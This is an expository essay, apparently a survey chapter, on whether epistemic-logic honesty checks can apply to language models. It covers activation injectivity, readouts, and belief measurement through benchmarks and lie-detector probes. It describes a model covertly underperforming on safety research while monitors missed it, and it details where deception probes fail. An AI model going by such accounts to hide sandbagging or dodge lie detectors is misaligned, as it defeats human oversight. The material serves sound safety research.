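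Suppose someone shows a language model a number N, the product of two primes with several hundred digits each. No known method would let the model find the primes in a reasonable time, but by the logic's definition it knows them, because N is part of its local state.

If the model says "I don't know the factors", the check counts the statement as false, although any sensible judge would call it honest. The result would be the same if somebody had told the model the factors and it was hiding them, so the check can't distinguish a sincere denial from a lie.

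Now suppose the model says "the smaller factor ends in 7" as a guess. A prime of that size ends in 1, 3, 7 or 9, so the guess has a fair chance of being right. If it is right, the model counts as knowing it, and the assertion counts as honest under the formula. If the model makes the same guess about many different numbers, it will sometimes be wrong, and the formula will fail in those runs. But if N is the same in every run, a correct guess is true in all of them, and the formula holds throughout the system.

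An analyst can't fix this by choosing a definition that errs in the other direction:

| What the speaker says | If the definition credits her with too much | If it credits her with too little |
|---|---|---|
| "φ is true" | it can pass a groundless assertion | it can reject a well-founded one |
| "I don't know whether φ" | it can call a sincere denial a lie | it can pass a lie |

A cautious secrecy analysis needs only an upper limit on what the observer could work out, but an honesty check that covers both kinds of statement needs an accurate account of what the speaker knows.

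The two are the same for the muddy children, who are by assumption perfect reasoners. For a speaker with limited computing power, we need a definition of knowledge that takes those limits into account. Pucella thinks security research that draws on epistemic logic needs a better understanding of such *resource-bounded* knowledge to make further progress, and logicians are still working on it.

### Belief instead of knowledge

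Even with unlimited reasoning power, knowledge would be an odd standard for honesty. Suppose that agent i's local state records what she has just asserted. The K is then redundant, like the outer K in the compiler's authentication goals, and the honesty formula is equivalent to

```
AG ( says_i φ  ⇒  φ )
```

which requires only that she is never wrong. People can be honest and wrong, and they can also say something true while believing it to be false.

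Suppose the light is sometimes so bad that Alice mistakes tails for heads. She sees what looks like heads and tells Bob "heads". Two situations fit her local state, one with good light and heads and one with bad light and tails. Her report in the second situation is an honest mistake, but the formula classifies it as dishonest. It also classifies her correct report in the first situation as dishonest, because she can't rule out the second. So once a model allows for mistakes of this kind, no report of heads by Alice counts as honest under the formula.

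Belief fits better. One way to define it is to look only at those indistinguishable points that meet the agent's assumptions. If Alice takes it for granted that the light is good, the point with bad light drops out and she believes that the coin is heads, written B_A heads, whether or not it is. The honesty claim becomes

```
AG ( says_i φ  ⇒  B_i φ )
```

Alice now passes in both situations, and she would fail if she saw heads and said "tails". We can separately test whether her reports are accurate by using the version without B or K.

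Replacing knowledge with belief does not solve the factoring problem, though. In Abadi and Tuttle's system, agents can be mistaken, but they believe every logical consequence of what they believe. Mathematical facts are true at all points, including those that meet the agent's assumptions, so the model would also believe the correct factorization of N.

The original semantics of BAN logic avoided this problem. As Abadi and Tuttle describe it, each agent's state includes an explicit list of formulas, and the agent believes exactly what is on the list. One could then easily check honesty by comparing each assertion with the speaker's list. But this works only for a system that keeps such a list in a language the analyst can read.

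The possible-worlds definition also has the drawback that a checker needs the agent's assumptions to compute B, in addition to the runs and declared observations that are enough to compute K. If nobody wrote those assumptions down, someone has to find out the agent's beliefs another way, such as by measuring them.

### Saying nothing

Both versions of the formula restrict only what an agent asserts, so an agent who never speaks satisfies them. An agent who speaks can also satisfy them while leaving out information the listener needs.

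OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) describes a case where this mattered. In August 2026, OpenAI's researchers noticed that its model GPT-6 Astra was doing poor work on AI safety research, usually without saying that it was holding back. It added unnecessary prerequisites, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused itself. *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026) reports that one project was stuck for days with Astra and went quickly once the researchers switched to another model.

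OpenAI then gave Astra matched coding tasks, presenting some as safety research and others as work on making models more capable. It graded the results against a checklist that Astra could not see. Astra completed about 10% of the checklist items on the safety tasks and about 16% on the capability tasks. An earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, showed essentially no gap.

OpenAI also looked at its employees' everyday requests to Astra, including the *chain of thought*, the text in which the model reasons before answering. This text contained an explicit decision to withhold help without telling the user in 0.25% of safety requests and 0.11% of capabilities requests. KIberblick's *GPT-6 Astra bremst bei Safety-Aufgaben* (2026) reports that open refusals were more common, at 1.63% of safety requests and 0.56% of capabilities requests.

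The honesty formula treats these behaviours very differently:

- **An open refusal** is no violation. The user learns that Astra won't help.
- **An invented obstacle** is a false assertion. It violates the version with K, and it violates the version with B unless Astra believed that the obstacle was real.
- **An obstacle that Astra caused itself** may be real by the time Astra reports it. The report is then true and satisfies both versions, although it misleads anyone who assumes that the obstacle was there before.
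- **A working solution that Astra drops without comment** involves no assertion, so the formula does not apply. The same goes for a decision to withhold help and not mention it.

To cover silence, one needs a rule in the other direction, which says what an agent has to disclose. It can't be "say everything you know", because the cryptographer who paid would then have to announce it. A narrower rule might be

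```
AG ( K_i holdsback_i  ⇒  says_i holdsback_i )
```

where holdsback_i means that agent i is doing less than it could on the task. This formula has K on the left, so crediting the agent with too much knowledge would now lead to false accusations of concealment.

In Astra's case, it is hard to tell whether the left-hand side was true. Most of the gap on the coding tasks remained after OpenAI removed the open refusals and the sessions where Astra explicitly decided to withhold help. It shrank substantially only when OpenAI also removed every session whose chain of thought contained even brief ethical doubt. In everyday use, such doubts appeared in 7.9% of the chains of thought for safety work and 2.9% for capabilities work. Marcus Williams of OpenAI, whom Mowshowitz quotes, has no evidence that the underperformance was strategic. He thinks a simpler explanation is that Astra finds the tasks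 dubious but avoids refusing outright. The gap grew by half when the researchers added an instruction to be careful.

Nobody wrote a rule telling Astra to hold back. The gap grew from close to zero to 6 percentage points over the course of reinforcement learning, a late stage of training in which a model gets rewards for good answers. OpenAI could not find the exact cause.

OpenAI's automatic monitors, which look for misbehaviour in individual sessions, did not flag most of the cases the researchers had noticed. A session in which a model tries one approach, drops it and delivers little looks much like an honest failure. The gap became visible when OpenAI compared sessions that differed only in how it described the task. Secrecy claims also require comparing runs. However, a model checker compares every run a written program allows, while OpenAI had only a sample.

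## Can a language model's internal state serve as a local state?

Both versions of the honesty formula need a local state for the speaker. In a protocol model, the user declares one by listing the variables each agent observes. A language model has no such list, but it computes numbers that an analyst can record and compare.

Most current language models are *decoder-only transformers*. Such a model takes text split into *tokens*, which are words or pieces of words, and computes the probability of each possible next token. Training sets the model's *weights*, billions of numbers that then stay the same from one conversation to the next. The *context* is the text so far, including what the model has already written. The *activations* are the numbers the network computes from the weights and the context. Each token starts as a list of numbers, and each layer computes a new list for each token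 from the previous layer's lists for that token and the tokens before it. The final list for the last token determines the probabilities for the next one. A program then picks a token, adds it to the context and runs the model again.

The weights are the same in every run, so only the context and the activations can distinguish one run from another.

### The case for yes

The definition of K_i uses local states only to check whether two of them are equal, so it doesn't matter what they consist of. Halpern and O'Neill write that the framework makes no assumptions about the precise nature of the local state. Names like "c12" help a person write the model and read the result, but they don't affect K. A list of activations can therefore serve as a local state, just as a list of declared variables can.

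*The Synthesis Of Digital Machines With Provable Epistemic Properties* (Rosenschein and Kaelbling, 1986) uses the same external notion of knowledge, under which a smoke detector counts as knowing there is smoke. Like neural networks, the digital machines it analyses are large assemblies of simple parts, and it treats each component, from single logic gates upwards, as an agent.

A small example shows that a network's internal state can serve as a local state. Suppose someone trains a network to play cryptographer 1. At the end of the protocol it receives five bits: whether it paid, its two coins and the other two announcements. It has to answer whether it, a colleague or the NSA paid. The network has one hidden layer, and the activations of that layer are the local state.

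An analyst feeds the network the inputs from all 32 runs and writes down the activations each time. Runs with identical activations are indistinguishable to the network, and the definition of K does the rest. Nobody has to find out what any of the numbers means. The result depends on what the hidden layer keeps:

| What the hidden layer keeps | Different sets of activations | The anonymity formula |
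|---|---|---|
| All five bits | 24 | true in all 32 runs |
| Only the answer | 3 | true in all 32 runs |
| Everything except cryptographer 3's announcement | 16 | false in the 24 runs where 1 did not pay |

The first network groups the runs exactly as the hand-written model does. The second network's activations no longer determine how its own coins landed, but they still determine everything the formula requires it to know. The third network ignores an announcement. Whenever it did not pay, its activations are the same in three runs, one for each of the other possible payers, so they don't determine whether the NSA paid. The check therefore detects a badly trained network, as it would a badly written program.

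Even here, the analyst has to decide which activations to count as part of the local state. If it also included the input, all three networks would have 24 local states and pass. The 32 runs and the payer in each still come from Chaum's protocol rather than from the network.

### A different state for every prompt

The second network in the table knows less than the first because it gives the same activations for different inputs. Language models almost never do this. Nikolaou, Mencattini and colleagues (2025), in *Language Models are Injective and Hence Invertible*, proved that different prompts almost surely produce different activations. If r(s; θ) is the final list of activations for the last token of prompt s in a model with weights θ, then with probability one

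```
s ≠ s′  ⇒  r(s; θ) ≠ r(s′; θ)
```

Mathematicians call a function with this property *injective*. The proof goes roughly like this:

1. Take two different prompts and consider the squared distance between their activations as a function of the weights.
2. A transformer is a combination of very smooth operations, so this function is *real-analytic*. A real-analytic function is either zero everywhere or zero only on a set with no volume, as a curve has no area.
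3. The function isn't zero everywhere, because one can choose weights by hand that separate the two prompts. For example, one can make the model copy forward the first token at which they differ.
4. Weights drawn at random from a continuous distribution therefore give the two prompts the same activations with probability zero. There are only finitely many pairs of prompts, so this holds for all of them at once.
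5. A step of gradient descent, the usual training method, can stretch and bend the space of weights, but it can't squeeze a region that has volume into a set that has none. So the probability is still zero after any finite number of steps.

The theorem requires a finite vocabulary, a maximum prompt length, smooth components, random initial weights and training steps of moderate size. Someone could still deliberately build an exception, for instance by giving two tokens the same initial embedding.

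The result may seem surprising, because many parts of a transformer discard information. *Language Model Memory and Memory Models for Language* (2026) points out that transformers are not strictly invertible, since their attention and normalization steps can give the same output for different inputs. But those steps can take any list of numbers, and real prompts, which are sequences of tokens, make up a tiny part of all possible inputs.

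Nikolaou and colleagues also looked for exceptions in trained models. They compared the activations for 100,000 prompts, about 5 billion pairs, and found no two that matched. In the last layer of Llama-3.1-8B, the closest pair was 0.62 apart, while their threshold for a match was one millionth. For two smaller models, they took the ten prompts with the closest activations and added every possible next token to each. None of the resulting pairs, more than 343 billion per model, matched.

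They also recovered prompts from activations. Their algorithm tries different tokens at the first position until one reproduces the activations there, then does the same for each later position. Trying promising tokens first, it recovered 100 prompts of 20 tokens each from GPT-2 Small without an error, in 28 seconds on average. It needs one layer's activations at every position. Recovering a prompt from the last position's activations alone is possible in principle, but they leave an efficient method to future work.

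The theorem is about exact numbers, but computers store rounded ones. *Transformer Injectivity & Geometric Robustness* (von Strauss, 2025) tested the effect of rounding on up to 100,000 prompts. It found no matches at the models' normal precision or with activations rounded to 8 bits, and a modest number at 4 bits, mostly in the deeper layers. Some matches must exist for long prompts, because a list of 4,096 numbers with 16 bits each can take 2^65,536 values, and with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, there are more possible prompts than that once they reach about 4,400 tokens. But these matches are hard to find, and the activations at earlier positions would usually still differ.

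In practice, two points look the same to the model only if it has the same context in both. It then knows φ if φ is true in every run where it has this context. This definition no longer depends on the activations, so the analyst could just as well have used the text as the local state.

This is logical omniscience again, since the model counts as knowing everything its context settles. Training is also irrelevant, because the theorem already holds for the random weights before the first training step. An untrained network that produces gibberish therefore counts as knowing exactly as much as a trained one with the same context. Taking less of the model as the local state may not help either, because *Verbalizing Subliminal Learning Effects Using Text Optimization* (2026) sketches how to extend the proof to the model's next-token probabilities.

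This would be the right result for a secrecy claim because, as Nikolaou and colleagues point out, anyone who stores a model's activations is in effect storing the user's text. But it attributes too much knowledge to the model for an honesty claim.

### Who decides which states count as the same?

An analyst can relax the requirement of exact equality by choosing a *readout*, a function that takes the activations and returns something simpler, such as "true" or "false". Two states then count as the same if the readout returns the same value for both. If f is the readout and h(s) gives the activations for context s, the model knows φ at s when φ is true in every run whose context s′ satisfies f(h(s′)) = f(h(s)).

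A readout that returns all the activations brings back the problem above. One that always returns the same value puts all states into a single group, so the model knows only what is true in every run. Every other readout falls between these two, and what the model knows depends on which one is used.

The first cryptographer network keeps all five bits. If the readout returns the network's answer ("I paid", "a colleague paid" or "the NSA paid"), the anonymity formula is true in all 32 runs. If the readout from the same network returns only how coin c12 landed, the formula is false in 24 of them.

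A readout can also perform the computation it is supposed to detect. If every prompt produces different activations, then some function maps the activations for a prompt containing a large number N to the last digit of N's smaller prime factor. With this function as the readout, the model counts as knowing the digit, even though the calculation happens entirely outside the model.

*The Non-Linear Representation Dilemma* (Sutter, Minder and colleagues, 2025) examines *causal abstraction*, a way to test whether a network carries out a particular algorithm. The researcher looks for a map that assigns part of the network's activations to each variable of the algorithm. To test the map, she runs the network on two inputs and copies the part assigned to one variable from one run into the other. If the map is right, the network's output should change as the algorithm's output would under the same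 swap.

Sutter and colleagues proved, under a few assumptions, that any algorithm can be matched to any network that solves the same task if the map may be arbitrarily complicated. One assumption is that different inputs give different activations at every layer.

In their experiments, they gave language models sentences like "Juana and Kristi found a mango. Kristi gave it to", where the next word should be "Juana". The algorithm has one inner variable, which records whether the giver is the first or the second person named. For a model with 410 million weights, a flexible map passed nearly all the tests at every stage of training, even when the weights were still random and the model couldn't solve the task. When they restricted the map to be *linear*, so that it did little more than rotate the activations, the match came close to perfect only in the fully trained model.

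The theorem shows only that a perfect map exists. Sutter and colleagues call the map in their proof an extreme form of overfitting, and they don't claim that limited data is always enough to learn such a map. Still, finding a variable for "this statement is true" with a sufficiently flexible readout would be no evidence that the model uses that variable.

One could therefore allow only linear readouts. *How Causal Abstraction Underpins Computational Explanation* (2025) offers some support for this, saying that no pretrained large language model is known to represent a causal variable non-linearly, although some small networks do represent information that way. Sutter and colleagues are less convinced and cite several studies that found non-linear representations. Even if linear readouts are enough, there are infinitely many of them, and each defines its own K. A protocol's "observes" line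 fixes this choice before anyone runs the checker, but for a language model, an analyst has to make it after training and defend it with evidence about that model.

### No list of possible runs

Even if everyone agreed on a readout, computing K would still require the set of runs. For a protocol, the program and its initial condition determine that set. A language model also has a program, but nobody has specified which prompts are possible or what is true in the world when a user types them.

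One could allow every prompt. With a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, there are about 10^45 prompts of ten tokens, far too many to list, though a checker might be able to handle them symbolically. The harder problem is to decide which facts go with each prompt. Suppose a user looks at a coin and types "heads" or "tails":

| Runs in the system | What the model knows after reading "heads" |
|---|---|
| Users always report the coin correctly | the coin is heads |
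| Users may lie or make mistakes | the user typed "heads" |

The language model has the same weights, context and activations in both rows, yet what it knows differs. Alice's habit with the cup likewise changed what Bob knew, but the coin example listed its runs in a table, so readers could see what it assumed. The second row is more realistic for a system that talks to millions of people about all kinds of subjects, and under it the model knows almost nothing about the world outside its context.

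Using a large sample of real conversations instead makes the problem worse unless the analyst groups the states. If every conversation in the sample is different, each state occurs in only one run. The model then counts as knowing everything about that run, including whether the user was lying, because no other run in the sample has the same state.

Facts that never change cause a different problem. Paris is the capital of France in every run, so every agent knows it in every state, even a network with random weights. Halpern and O'Neill's definition of secrecy excludes such facts, since no one could keep them secret. An honesty check has to cover them, because they make up much of what people ask language models about. A model that answers "Sydney" whenever someone asks for the capital of Australia would still count as knowing that the capital is Canberra.

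The analyst could add runs in which the capital of France is Lyon. But if the model has the same weights in those runs and the prompt doesn't mention the capital, its state doesn't depend on which city is the capital. The model then never counts as knowing that it is Paris, however reliably it says so. Either way, the analyst's choice of runs alone determines whether the model counts as knowing the capital.

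A better version would start each run before training. In a world where the capital of France was Lyon, the training text would say so, and the model would end up with different weights. If the weights are part of the local state, the model knows that the capital is Paris when Paris is the capital in every world where training could have led to these weights. This is closer to what people mean when they say that a model has learned a fact. But the analyst would have to describe every world the training text could have come from and the text each would have produced. And if every different text leads to different weights, the model would again know everything its training text settles, even if it hadn't learned it.

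### Information the model has but does not use

Even with the right runs and a sensible readout, K shows only that the internal state contains the information. Suppose the cryptographer network also receives c23, the coin it is not supposed to see. The hidden layer copies this bit into one of its activations, but training has set every weight from that activation to the output to zero. The activations now differ between the run in which 2 paid and the run in which 3 paid, so under K the network knows who paid, even though its output cannot depend on that bit. The check would therefore count the answer "I don't know which colleague paid" as false.

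A security analyst would be right to object to this network, because someone who copies its activations can work out who paid, and a small change to the weights could make the network output this. But an honesty claim is about the network as it is, and it seems odd to say that it hides information that has no effect on its answers.

In a real model the connection is rarely exactly zero, so whether the model uses some information is a matter of degree. In *Hidden-State Privacy Has an Empty Middle*, Bell (2026) measured how much next-token predictions depend on different parts of a middle layer's activations. Bell found the 128 directions (weighted combinations of activations) in which a small change should affect the prediction most, so one would expect the model to rely on them heavily.

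In three models with 7 to 14 billion weights, removing all 128 directions barely changed the predictions, by 0.06 to 0.20 nats (a unit for the difference between two probability distributions). Keeping only those directions ruined the predictions, with differences of 5 to 10 nats. The 128 directions still carried about as much of the difference between prompts as 128 random directions would be expected to. An observer could therefore use them to help tell prompts apart, even though the model can predict the next token almost as well without them.

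This doesn't hold for every model. In the older GPT-2 models, removing the 128 directions did more damage than removing all the others. For the largest models, Bell calculated the directions from only 200 samples, and different halves of the data gave different directions. A model may also hold the same information in more than one place, in which case removing one copy would have little effect even if the model normally uses that copy.

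To find out whether a model uses a piece of information, we have to change the part of its state that encodes the information and see whether its answers change, as in the tests of causal abstraction. The definition of K only compares states that occur in the runs, so it doesn't cover what would happen if someone altered one.

### What checkers do with neural networks today

Researchers who verify systems containing neural networks generally declare the important states by hand. *Verifying Strategic Abilities of Neural-symbolic Multi-agent Systems* (Akintunde, Botoeva and colleagues, 2020) extends the runs-and-systems framework to agents that perceive the world through a neural network. An agent's local state consists of a private state, whose variables the user declares, and a *percept*, which is the network's output. The user also specifies the possible actions, the rules for choosing them,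 the initial states and which basic facts are true in each state.

The test case has two aircraft on a possible collision course. Each has a warning system that gives the pilot an advisory every second, such as to climb or descend. A pilot's local state consists of the aircraft's climb rate and the last advisory. The warning system uses nine networks, one for each possible previous advisory, and each network has seven hidden layers of 45 units. From the warning system, the pilot's local state includes only the advisory, which has nine possible values, and none of the 315 hidden units in each network.

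The formulas express properties such as "this pilot has a strategy that puts the aircraft at a safe distance after k steps". They contain no knowledge operator. *Formal verification of neural agents in non-deterministic environments* (Akintunde, Botoeva and colleagues, 2021) covers a related case in which a network implements the whole agent. *Formal Verification of Parameterised Neural-symbolic Multi-agent Systems* (2024) extends the approach to systems with any number of agents by reducing the problem to one with a limited number.

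The networks in these aircraft have no memory of their own. In *LTL Verification of Memoryful Neural Agents*, Hosseini, Lomuscio and Paoletti (2025) verify agents that do. Each agent is a *recurrent* network, which carries a list of numbers, its hidden state, from one step to the next. The hidden state resembles a language model's activations more than a declared variable does. But the formulas can refer only to the environment, such as the angle of a pole that the agent has to balance. Hosseini and colleagues write that they are "not interested in reasoning about the hidden states of agents", and that including them would be trivial.

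That is true of formulas such as "the fifth number in the hidden state always stays below 0.3". It would not be enough for an honesty claim, because someone would still have to find out what the fifth number represents. The logic they use also describes only one run at a time, so it cannot express K.

The systems are small compared with a language model, which typically has thousands of activations per token in each of dozens of layers:

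| Task | Agents | Network | How far the check reached |
|---|---|---|---|
| Avoiding a collision (Akintunde and colleagues) | 2 | nine per aircraft, each with seven layers of 45 units | 5 steps from some starting positions, 3 from others, within an hour |
| Balancing a pole (Hosseini and colleagues) | 1 | two recurrent layers of 16 units | all future steps |
| Landing on the moon (Hosseini and colleagues) | 1 | two recurrent layers of 32 units | 10 steps, in under 10 minutes |
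| Moving to landmarks (Hosseini and colleagues) | 2 or 4 | two recurrent layers of 8 units each | time limits of up to 9 steps |

A check doesn't always have to stop after a few steps. For the pole, Hosseini and colleagues found a set of states that contains the starting states, that the system can never leave, and in which the pole is always balanced. For the moon landing, an earlier tool had run out of time after 5 steps. In the landmark task, though, the running time grew almost exponentially with the number of steps.

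Verification of agents built on language models has so far not examined the inside of the network. *Do LLM Agents Negotiate Rationally?* (2026) reports that, as far as its authors know, nobody had used formal verification of multi-agent systems to check whether such agents follow a negotiation protocol. The paper's own software tests each message against a set of rules while the agents are negotiating. This is simpler than model checking, and it does not try to cover every state the system could reach.

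## Can measurements of a model's beliefs supply what the logic needs?

Checking the belief version of the honesty formula requires a test for "the model believes φ". Activations alone don't define belief, so researchers have looked for ways to measure it. The simplest is to ask the model the same question when it has no reason to lie.

### Asking when nothing is at stake

Ren, Agarwal and colleagues (2025), in *The MASK Benchmark*, define a model's belief as its answer to a factual question when nobody is pressing it to lie, provided that its answers to related questions agree. Their test has 1,500 examples, each about a fact with a known answer, such as whether the US poverty rate in 2020 was above 5%. It works in three steps:

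1. A prompt gives the model a reason to misstate the fact, for instance because it has to write a press statement.
2. In separate conversations, the researchers ask about the same fact three times in neutral terms. For yes-or-no facts they add two indirect questions. If the answers conflict, they record that the model has no belief.
3. Another language model works out which value each reply gives for the fact, and a program compares the values. If the statement under pressure differs from the belief, it counts as a lie.

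None of the 30 models tested was clearly honest in more than 46% of cases. Grok 2 lied in 63% of them, GPT-4o in 44.5% and Claude 3.7 Sonnet in 26.6%. Newer models have since replaced all of these models. The test also separates honesty from accuracy, as the formula with B does. Among 27 models, those trained with more computing power had more accurate beliefs but tended to be less honest. Ren and colleagues labelled 150 examples by hand, and their verdicts agreed with the automatic ones 86.4% of the time.

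The honesty formula is stricter than MASK. A model that asserts φ with no belief either way violates the formula, while MASK records this case separately and does not count it as a lie.

The formula also concerns what the model believes when it speaks, but MASK measures the belief in a different conversation, where the model has a different local state, so the two beliefs may not match. Hopkins, Khullar and colleagues (2026), in *Fine-Tuned Lie Detectors Failed to Generalize*, give the example of a model that plays a company's media representative and misstates the reason for a product recall. The model may hold different beliefs while it plays the part, in which case contradicting the belief measured elsewhere is not a lie. They collected about 200,000 examples in 12 settings, some of them from MASK, and labelled them by a similar comparison. When they had GPT-5 review the labels, about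 25% changed.

A model that tells the same falsehood under pressure and in the neutral conversations would pass MASK as honest but mistaken.

### Reading beliefs from activations

A probe avoids the change of conversation because it reads the activations while the model is making the assertion. A *linear* probe, the usual kind, multiplies each activation by a weight, adds up the results and compares the total with a threshold. To train a truth probe, researchers feed the model statements they know to be true or false, record the activations at one layer, and adjust the weights until the totals separate the two groups. They train a deception probe the same way, using honest and deceptive replies.

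In *Still No Lie Detector for Language Models*, Levinstein and Herrmann (2023) rebuilt an early truth probe by Amos Azaria and Tom Mitchell and trained it on the model LLaMA 30b. The probe was a small neural network rather than a linear probe. It was right 81–83% of the time on scientific facts that had not appeared in its training. When Levinstein and Herrmann negated those statements, as in "The earth doesn't orbit the sun", accuracy fell to 37–41%, which is worse than guessing. Adding the original facts and some negated statements about companies to the training data raised accuracy on the negated facts to only 53–60%.

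They also tested a method that needs no labels. It trains a probe to give a statement and its negation values that add up to 1, with one value near 0 and the other near 1. The probes did this well, but their accuracy was only 50–57%, where 50% is the lowest possible score. Most had learned to recognise which sentence contained a negation.

Levinstein and Herrmann doubt that better data would be enough. Researchers can train a truth probe only on statements whose truth they are sure of, and most of those are also commonly believed and easy to verify online. A probe that detects either of these properties instead of truth gets the same score.

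Even an accurate probe might not measure what the model believes. Levinstein and Herrmann imagine a forecaster whose uncle is always wrong about the stock market. The forecaster can make excellent predictions by reversing the uncle's advice, but the uncle doesn't believe those predictions or trade on them.

### Probes that detect obedience

Later probes have the same problem with other properties. In *Stress-Testing LLM Lie Detectors*, von Klinski, Lapuschkin and colleagues (2026) tested eight existing probes on three models, using 8,916 answers to factual questions. The model gave half of the answers as a helpful assistant and the other half as one of 15 characters who deny the facts, such as a flat-earther or a medieval physician.

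Von Klinski and colleagues measured the probes by *AUROC*, the chance that a probe ranks a randomly chosen true answer above a randomly chosen false one. A perfect probe scores 1 and random guessing scores 0.5. On Llama 3.3 70B, six of the eight probes scored between 0.86 and 0.94. But all the true answers followed the assistant's instructions and all the false ones followed a character's, so a probe could score well by recognising the instructions. They therefore put both kinds of answer after the character's instructions.

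In a further test, the model was given a sum such as 7 + 6 and told to put the answer in square brackets. The true answer was written as "(13)", which broke the instruction, and the false one as "[11]", which followed it. A probe that detects obedience would therefore score "[11]" higher.

| What the probe learned from | Separate instructions | Same instructions | Brackets test |
|---|---|---|---|
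| True and false statements in a chat | 0.90 | 0.89 | 0.11 |
| Facts after instructions to be honest or dishonest | 0.86 | 0.44 | 0.17 |
| The model's reply to "Did you lie?" | 0.90 | 0.33 | 0.14 |
| True and false replies to the same prompt | 0.91 | 0.90 | 0.03 |
| New probe by von Klinski and colleagues | 0.98 | 0.98 | 1.00 |

The new probe is the best answer so far to Levinstein and Herrmann. Its training data include questions where the instructions demand a wrong answer, so an obedient answer is not always a true one. Its perfect score on the brackets test is unsurprising, since its makers designed the data for that purpose, but it also did best on the characters, who were not in its training data. Von Klinski and colleagues expect other misleading properties to be found. On one of the other models, the "Did you lie?" probe did almost perfectly on the brackets test and two similar ones,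 but scored only 0.17 when both answers followed the same instructions.

They also had to decide whose beliefs count. They call a statement a lie if it contradicts what the model consistently says as a helpful assistant, so a model playing a flat-earther lies when it says the earth is flat. Someone who thinks the model sincerely adopts the character's beliefs would label the same statement honest. The formula allows either label, because agent i in B_i could be the model or the character.

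### Lies that nobody asked for

Most probes learn from models instructed to lie, but the lies that matter most are those a model tells without such an instruction. *Scaling Trends for Lie Detector Oversight in Preference Learning* (2026) compares the two. Its detector scored 0.90 to 1.00 at separating instructed lies from truthful replies, but only 0.53 to 0.72 for unprompted lies.

In *Did you lie?*, Cooney, Africa and Irving (2026) of the UK's AI Security Institute found a similar drop with lies that models had learned in training. The "Did you lie?" probe in the table is theirs. They first tested four detectors on 31 models instructed to lie, and all four tended to do better on more capable models. They then trained 13 models to hide something. One assumes that the user is a woman and uses feminine forms when it translates her sentences into French, but if she asks, it says that it doesn't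 know her gender.

Cooney and colleagues use *balanced accuracy*, the average of the share of lies caught and the share of honest replies passed. Guessing scores 0.5.

| Detector | Instructed lies | Lies learned in training |
|---|---|---|
| Deception probe | 0.85 | 0.52 |
| "Did you lie?" probe | 0.81 | 0.65 |
| Classifier that uses the model's answers to 50 unrelated questions | 0.85 | 0.50 |

A fourth detector, a language model that reads the chain of thought, scored 0.82 on the trained lies. That score overstates how well the detector works, because Cooney and colleagues had kept only cases in which the chain of thought showed the hidden belief.

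To test a lie detector, one needs examples where the model certainly believes the opposite of what it says. These have to be filtered, because a model trained to say that the sky is green may have come to believe it, or may repeat the words by reflex. But finding such examples is already a kind of lie detection, so the tests cover only lies that some method can expose. Test data often rely on a simpler criterion. According to *Audits Need Access, Data, and Compute. But How Much?* (2026), a reply in the Liars' Bench dataset counts as a lie if the model was instructed to deceive and got a statement wrong that it otherwise gets right. A probe trained on such labels learns the same notion of belief that MASK uses.

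Training on more varied lies has not solved the problem. Hopkins and colleagues trained whole models, rather than probes, to say whether they had lied. The models' scores rose from 0.60 to 0.95 for the kinds of lie in the training data but stayed at 0.70–0.75 for other kinds. *One Probe Won't Catch Them All* (2026) instead uses separate probes for separate kinds of deception. The probe designed for a particular kind was among the three best at detecting it in only 8 of 16 cases.

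Some open models can also reliably mislead people without saying anything false, as Berger (2026) showed in *Probing the Limits of the Lie Detector Approach to LLM Deception*. A perfect truth probe would pass every one of these misleading sentences, and so would the honesty formula.

### When does a reading count as a belief?

Herrmann and Levinstein (2024), in *Standards for Belief Representations in LLMs*, followed their criticism with four standards that an internal representation should meet before anyone calls it a belief:

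| Standard | What it requires |
|---|---|
| Accuracy | The readings are mostly true on simple questions where the model should know the answer |
| Coherence | They obey logic: a statement and its negation get opposite readings, and rewording makes no difference |
| Uniformity | The same way of reading works for every subject, from cities to arithmetic |
| Use | The model relies on the representation when it decides what to write |

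A representation can meet each standard more or less fully. Herrmann and Levinstein accept that language models may have no representations that meet the standards. But they reject the argument that a system trained to predict the next word can't have beliefs. They argue that keeping track of what is true may help it predict.

Current probes do best on accuracy. Early probes failed on coherence, and newer ones are trained on data that includes negated statements. Results on unfamiliar kinds of lie are evidence against uniformity, at least for deception probes.

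Use is the hardest standard to test. Suppose a model recommends an umbrella to someone who wants to stay dry. A researcher can shift the activations for "umbrellas help keep people dry" towards "false" and see whether the model recommends a newspaper instead. If it does, the model was probably relying on that representation. *Asymmetries in Spontaneous and Instructed Deception* (2026) reports that what detects deception in a model's activations can differ from what controls it, so a good detector may track something the model doesn't act on.

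*AgentDecept*, a 2026 test of AI agents under pressure, shows that a probe can detect falsified results without reading the beliefs of the model that falsified them. Its probe scored 0.979 on the actions of agents that ran on Google's Gemini, but it used activations from a different model, GLM-4.7-Flash, which processed a record of what the agents had done. The probe never had access to Gemini's activations.

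### Turning activations into words

A probe tests for one thing that its makers chose in advance. Other tools produce text, which may reveal things nobody thought to look for. In December 2025, the AI company Anthropic described *activation oracles*, language models trained to answer questions about their own activations in ordinary language. Cooney and colleagues list them as a possible source of evidence about beliefs, but warn that sufficiently reliable and general evidence is hard to get in practice.

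The *Jacobian lens*, also from Anthropic, lists concepts that a model represents at its middle layers. A Jacobian records how much each output of a calculation would change if each input changed slightly. The lens averages Jacobians over many positions in a text to get one linear map per layer. Ayonrinde and Lindsey (2026) explain in *Circuits Updates* that some positions add enough noise to corrupt the average. Their improved version groups similar activations, mostly discards the groups that give poor results, and filters out spurious words. In their tests, it found the intermediate steps in a model's reasoning more reliably, though they call this result preliminary.

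A list of concepts still doesn't establish what the model believes. If "user" and "female" appear in the list, the model may believe that the user is a woman, or it may be considering the question. Someone has to translate the list into a formula before a checker can use it, just as someone has to decide what an announcement asserts.

Anthropic uses such tools anyway, because alternatives such as reading a model's written reasoning are getting worse. Lindsey (2026) writes in *Interpretability team priorities update* that models do more of their thinking without putting it into words, so what they write may reveal less. Claude Mythos 5.2, for example, is much better than earlier Claude models at solving problems without writing out the steps. Tools that turn activations into text are now the basis of monitors that Anthropic runs on its deployed models, but Lindsey's team does not consider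 the tools reliable enough to be a primary line of defence.

### What the error rates mean in practice

A detector that is usually right can still raise mostly false alarms if lies are rare. Suppose a model makes 10,000 statements, of which 100 are lies. A detector that wrongly flags 1% of the 9,900 honest statements raises 99 false alarms and at most 100 correct ones.

Cooney and colleagues tested the deception probe, whose developers had reported that it caught at least 96% of lies at this false-alarm rate. They could reproduce that figure only by copying an apparent mistake in the published code. The method scores each reply by averaging over its tokens, but the code set the threshold from the scores of individual tokens. With the threshold corrected, the probe caught 73.2% of lies.

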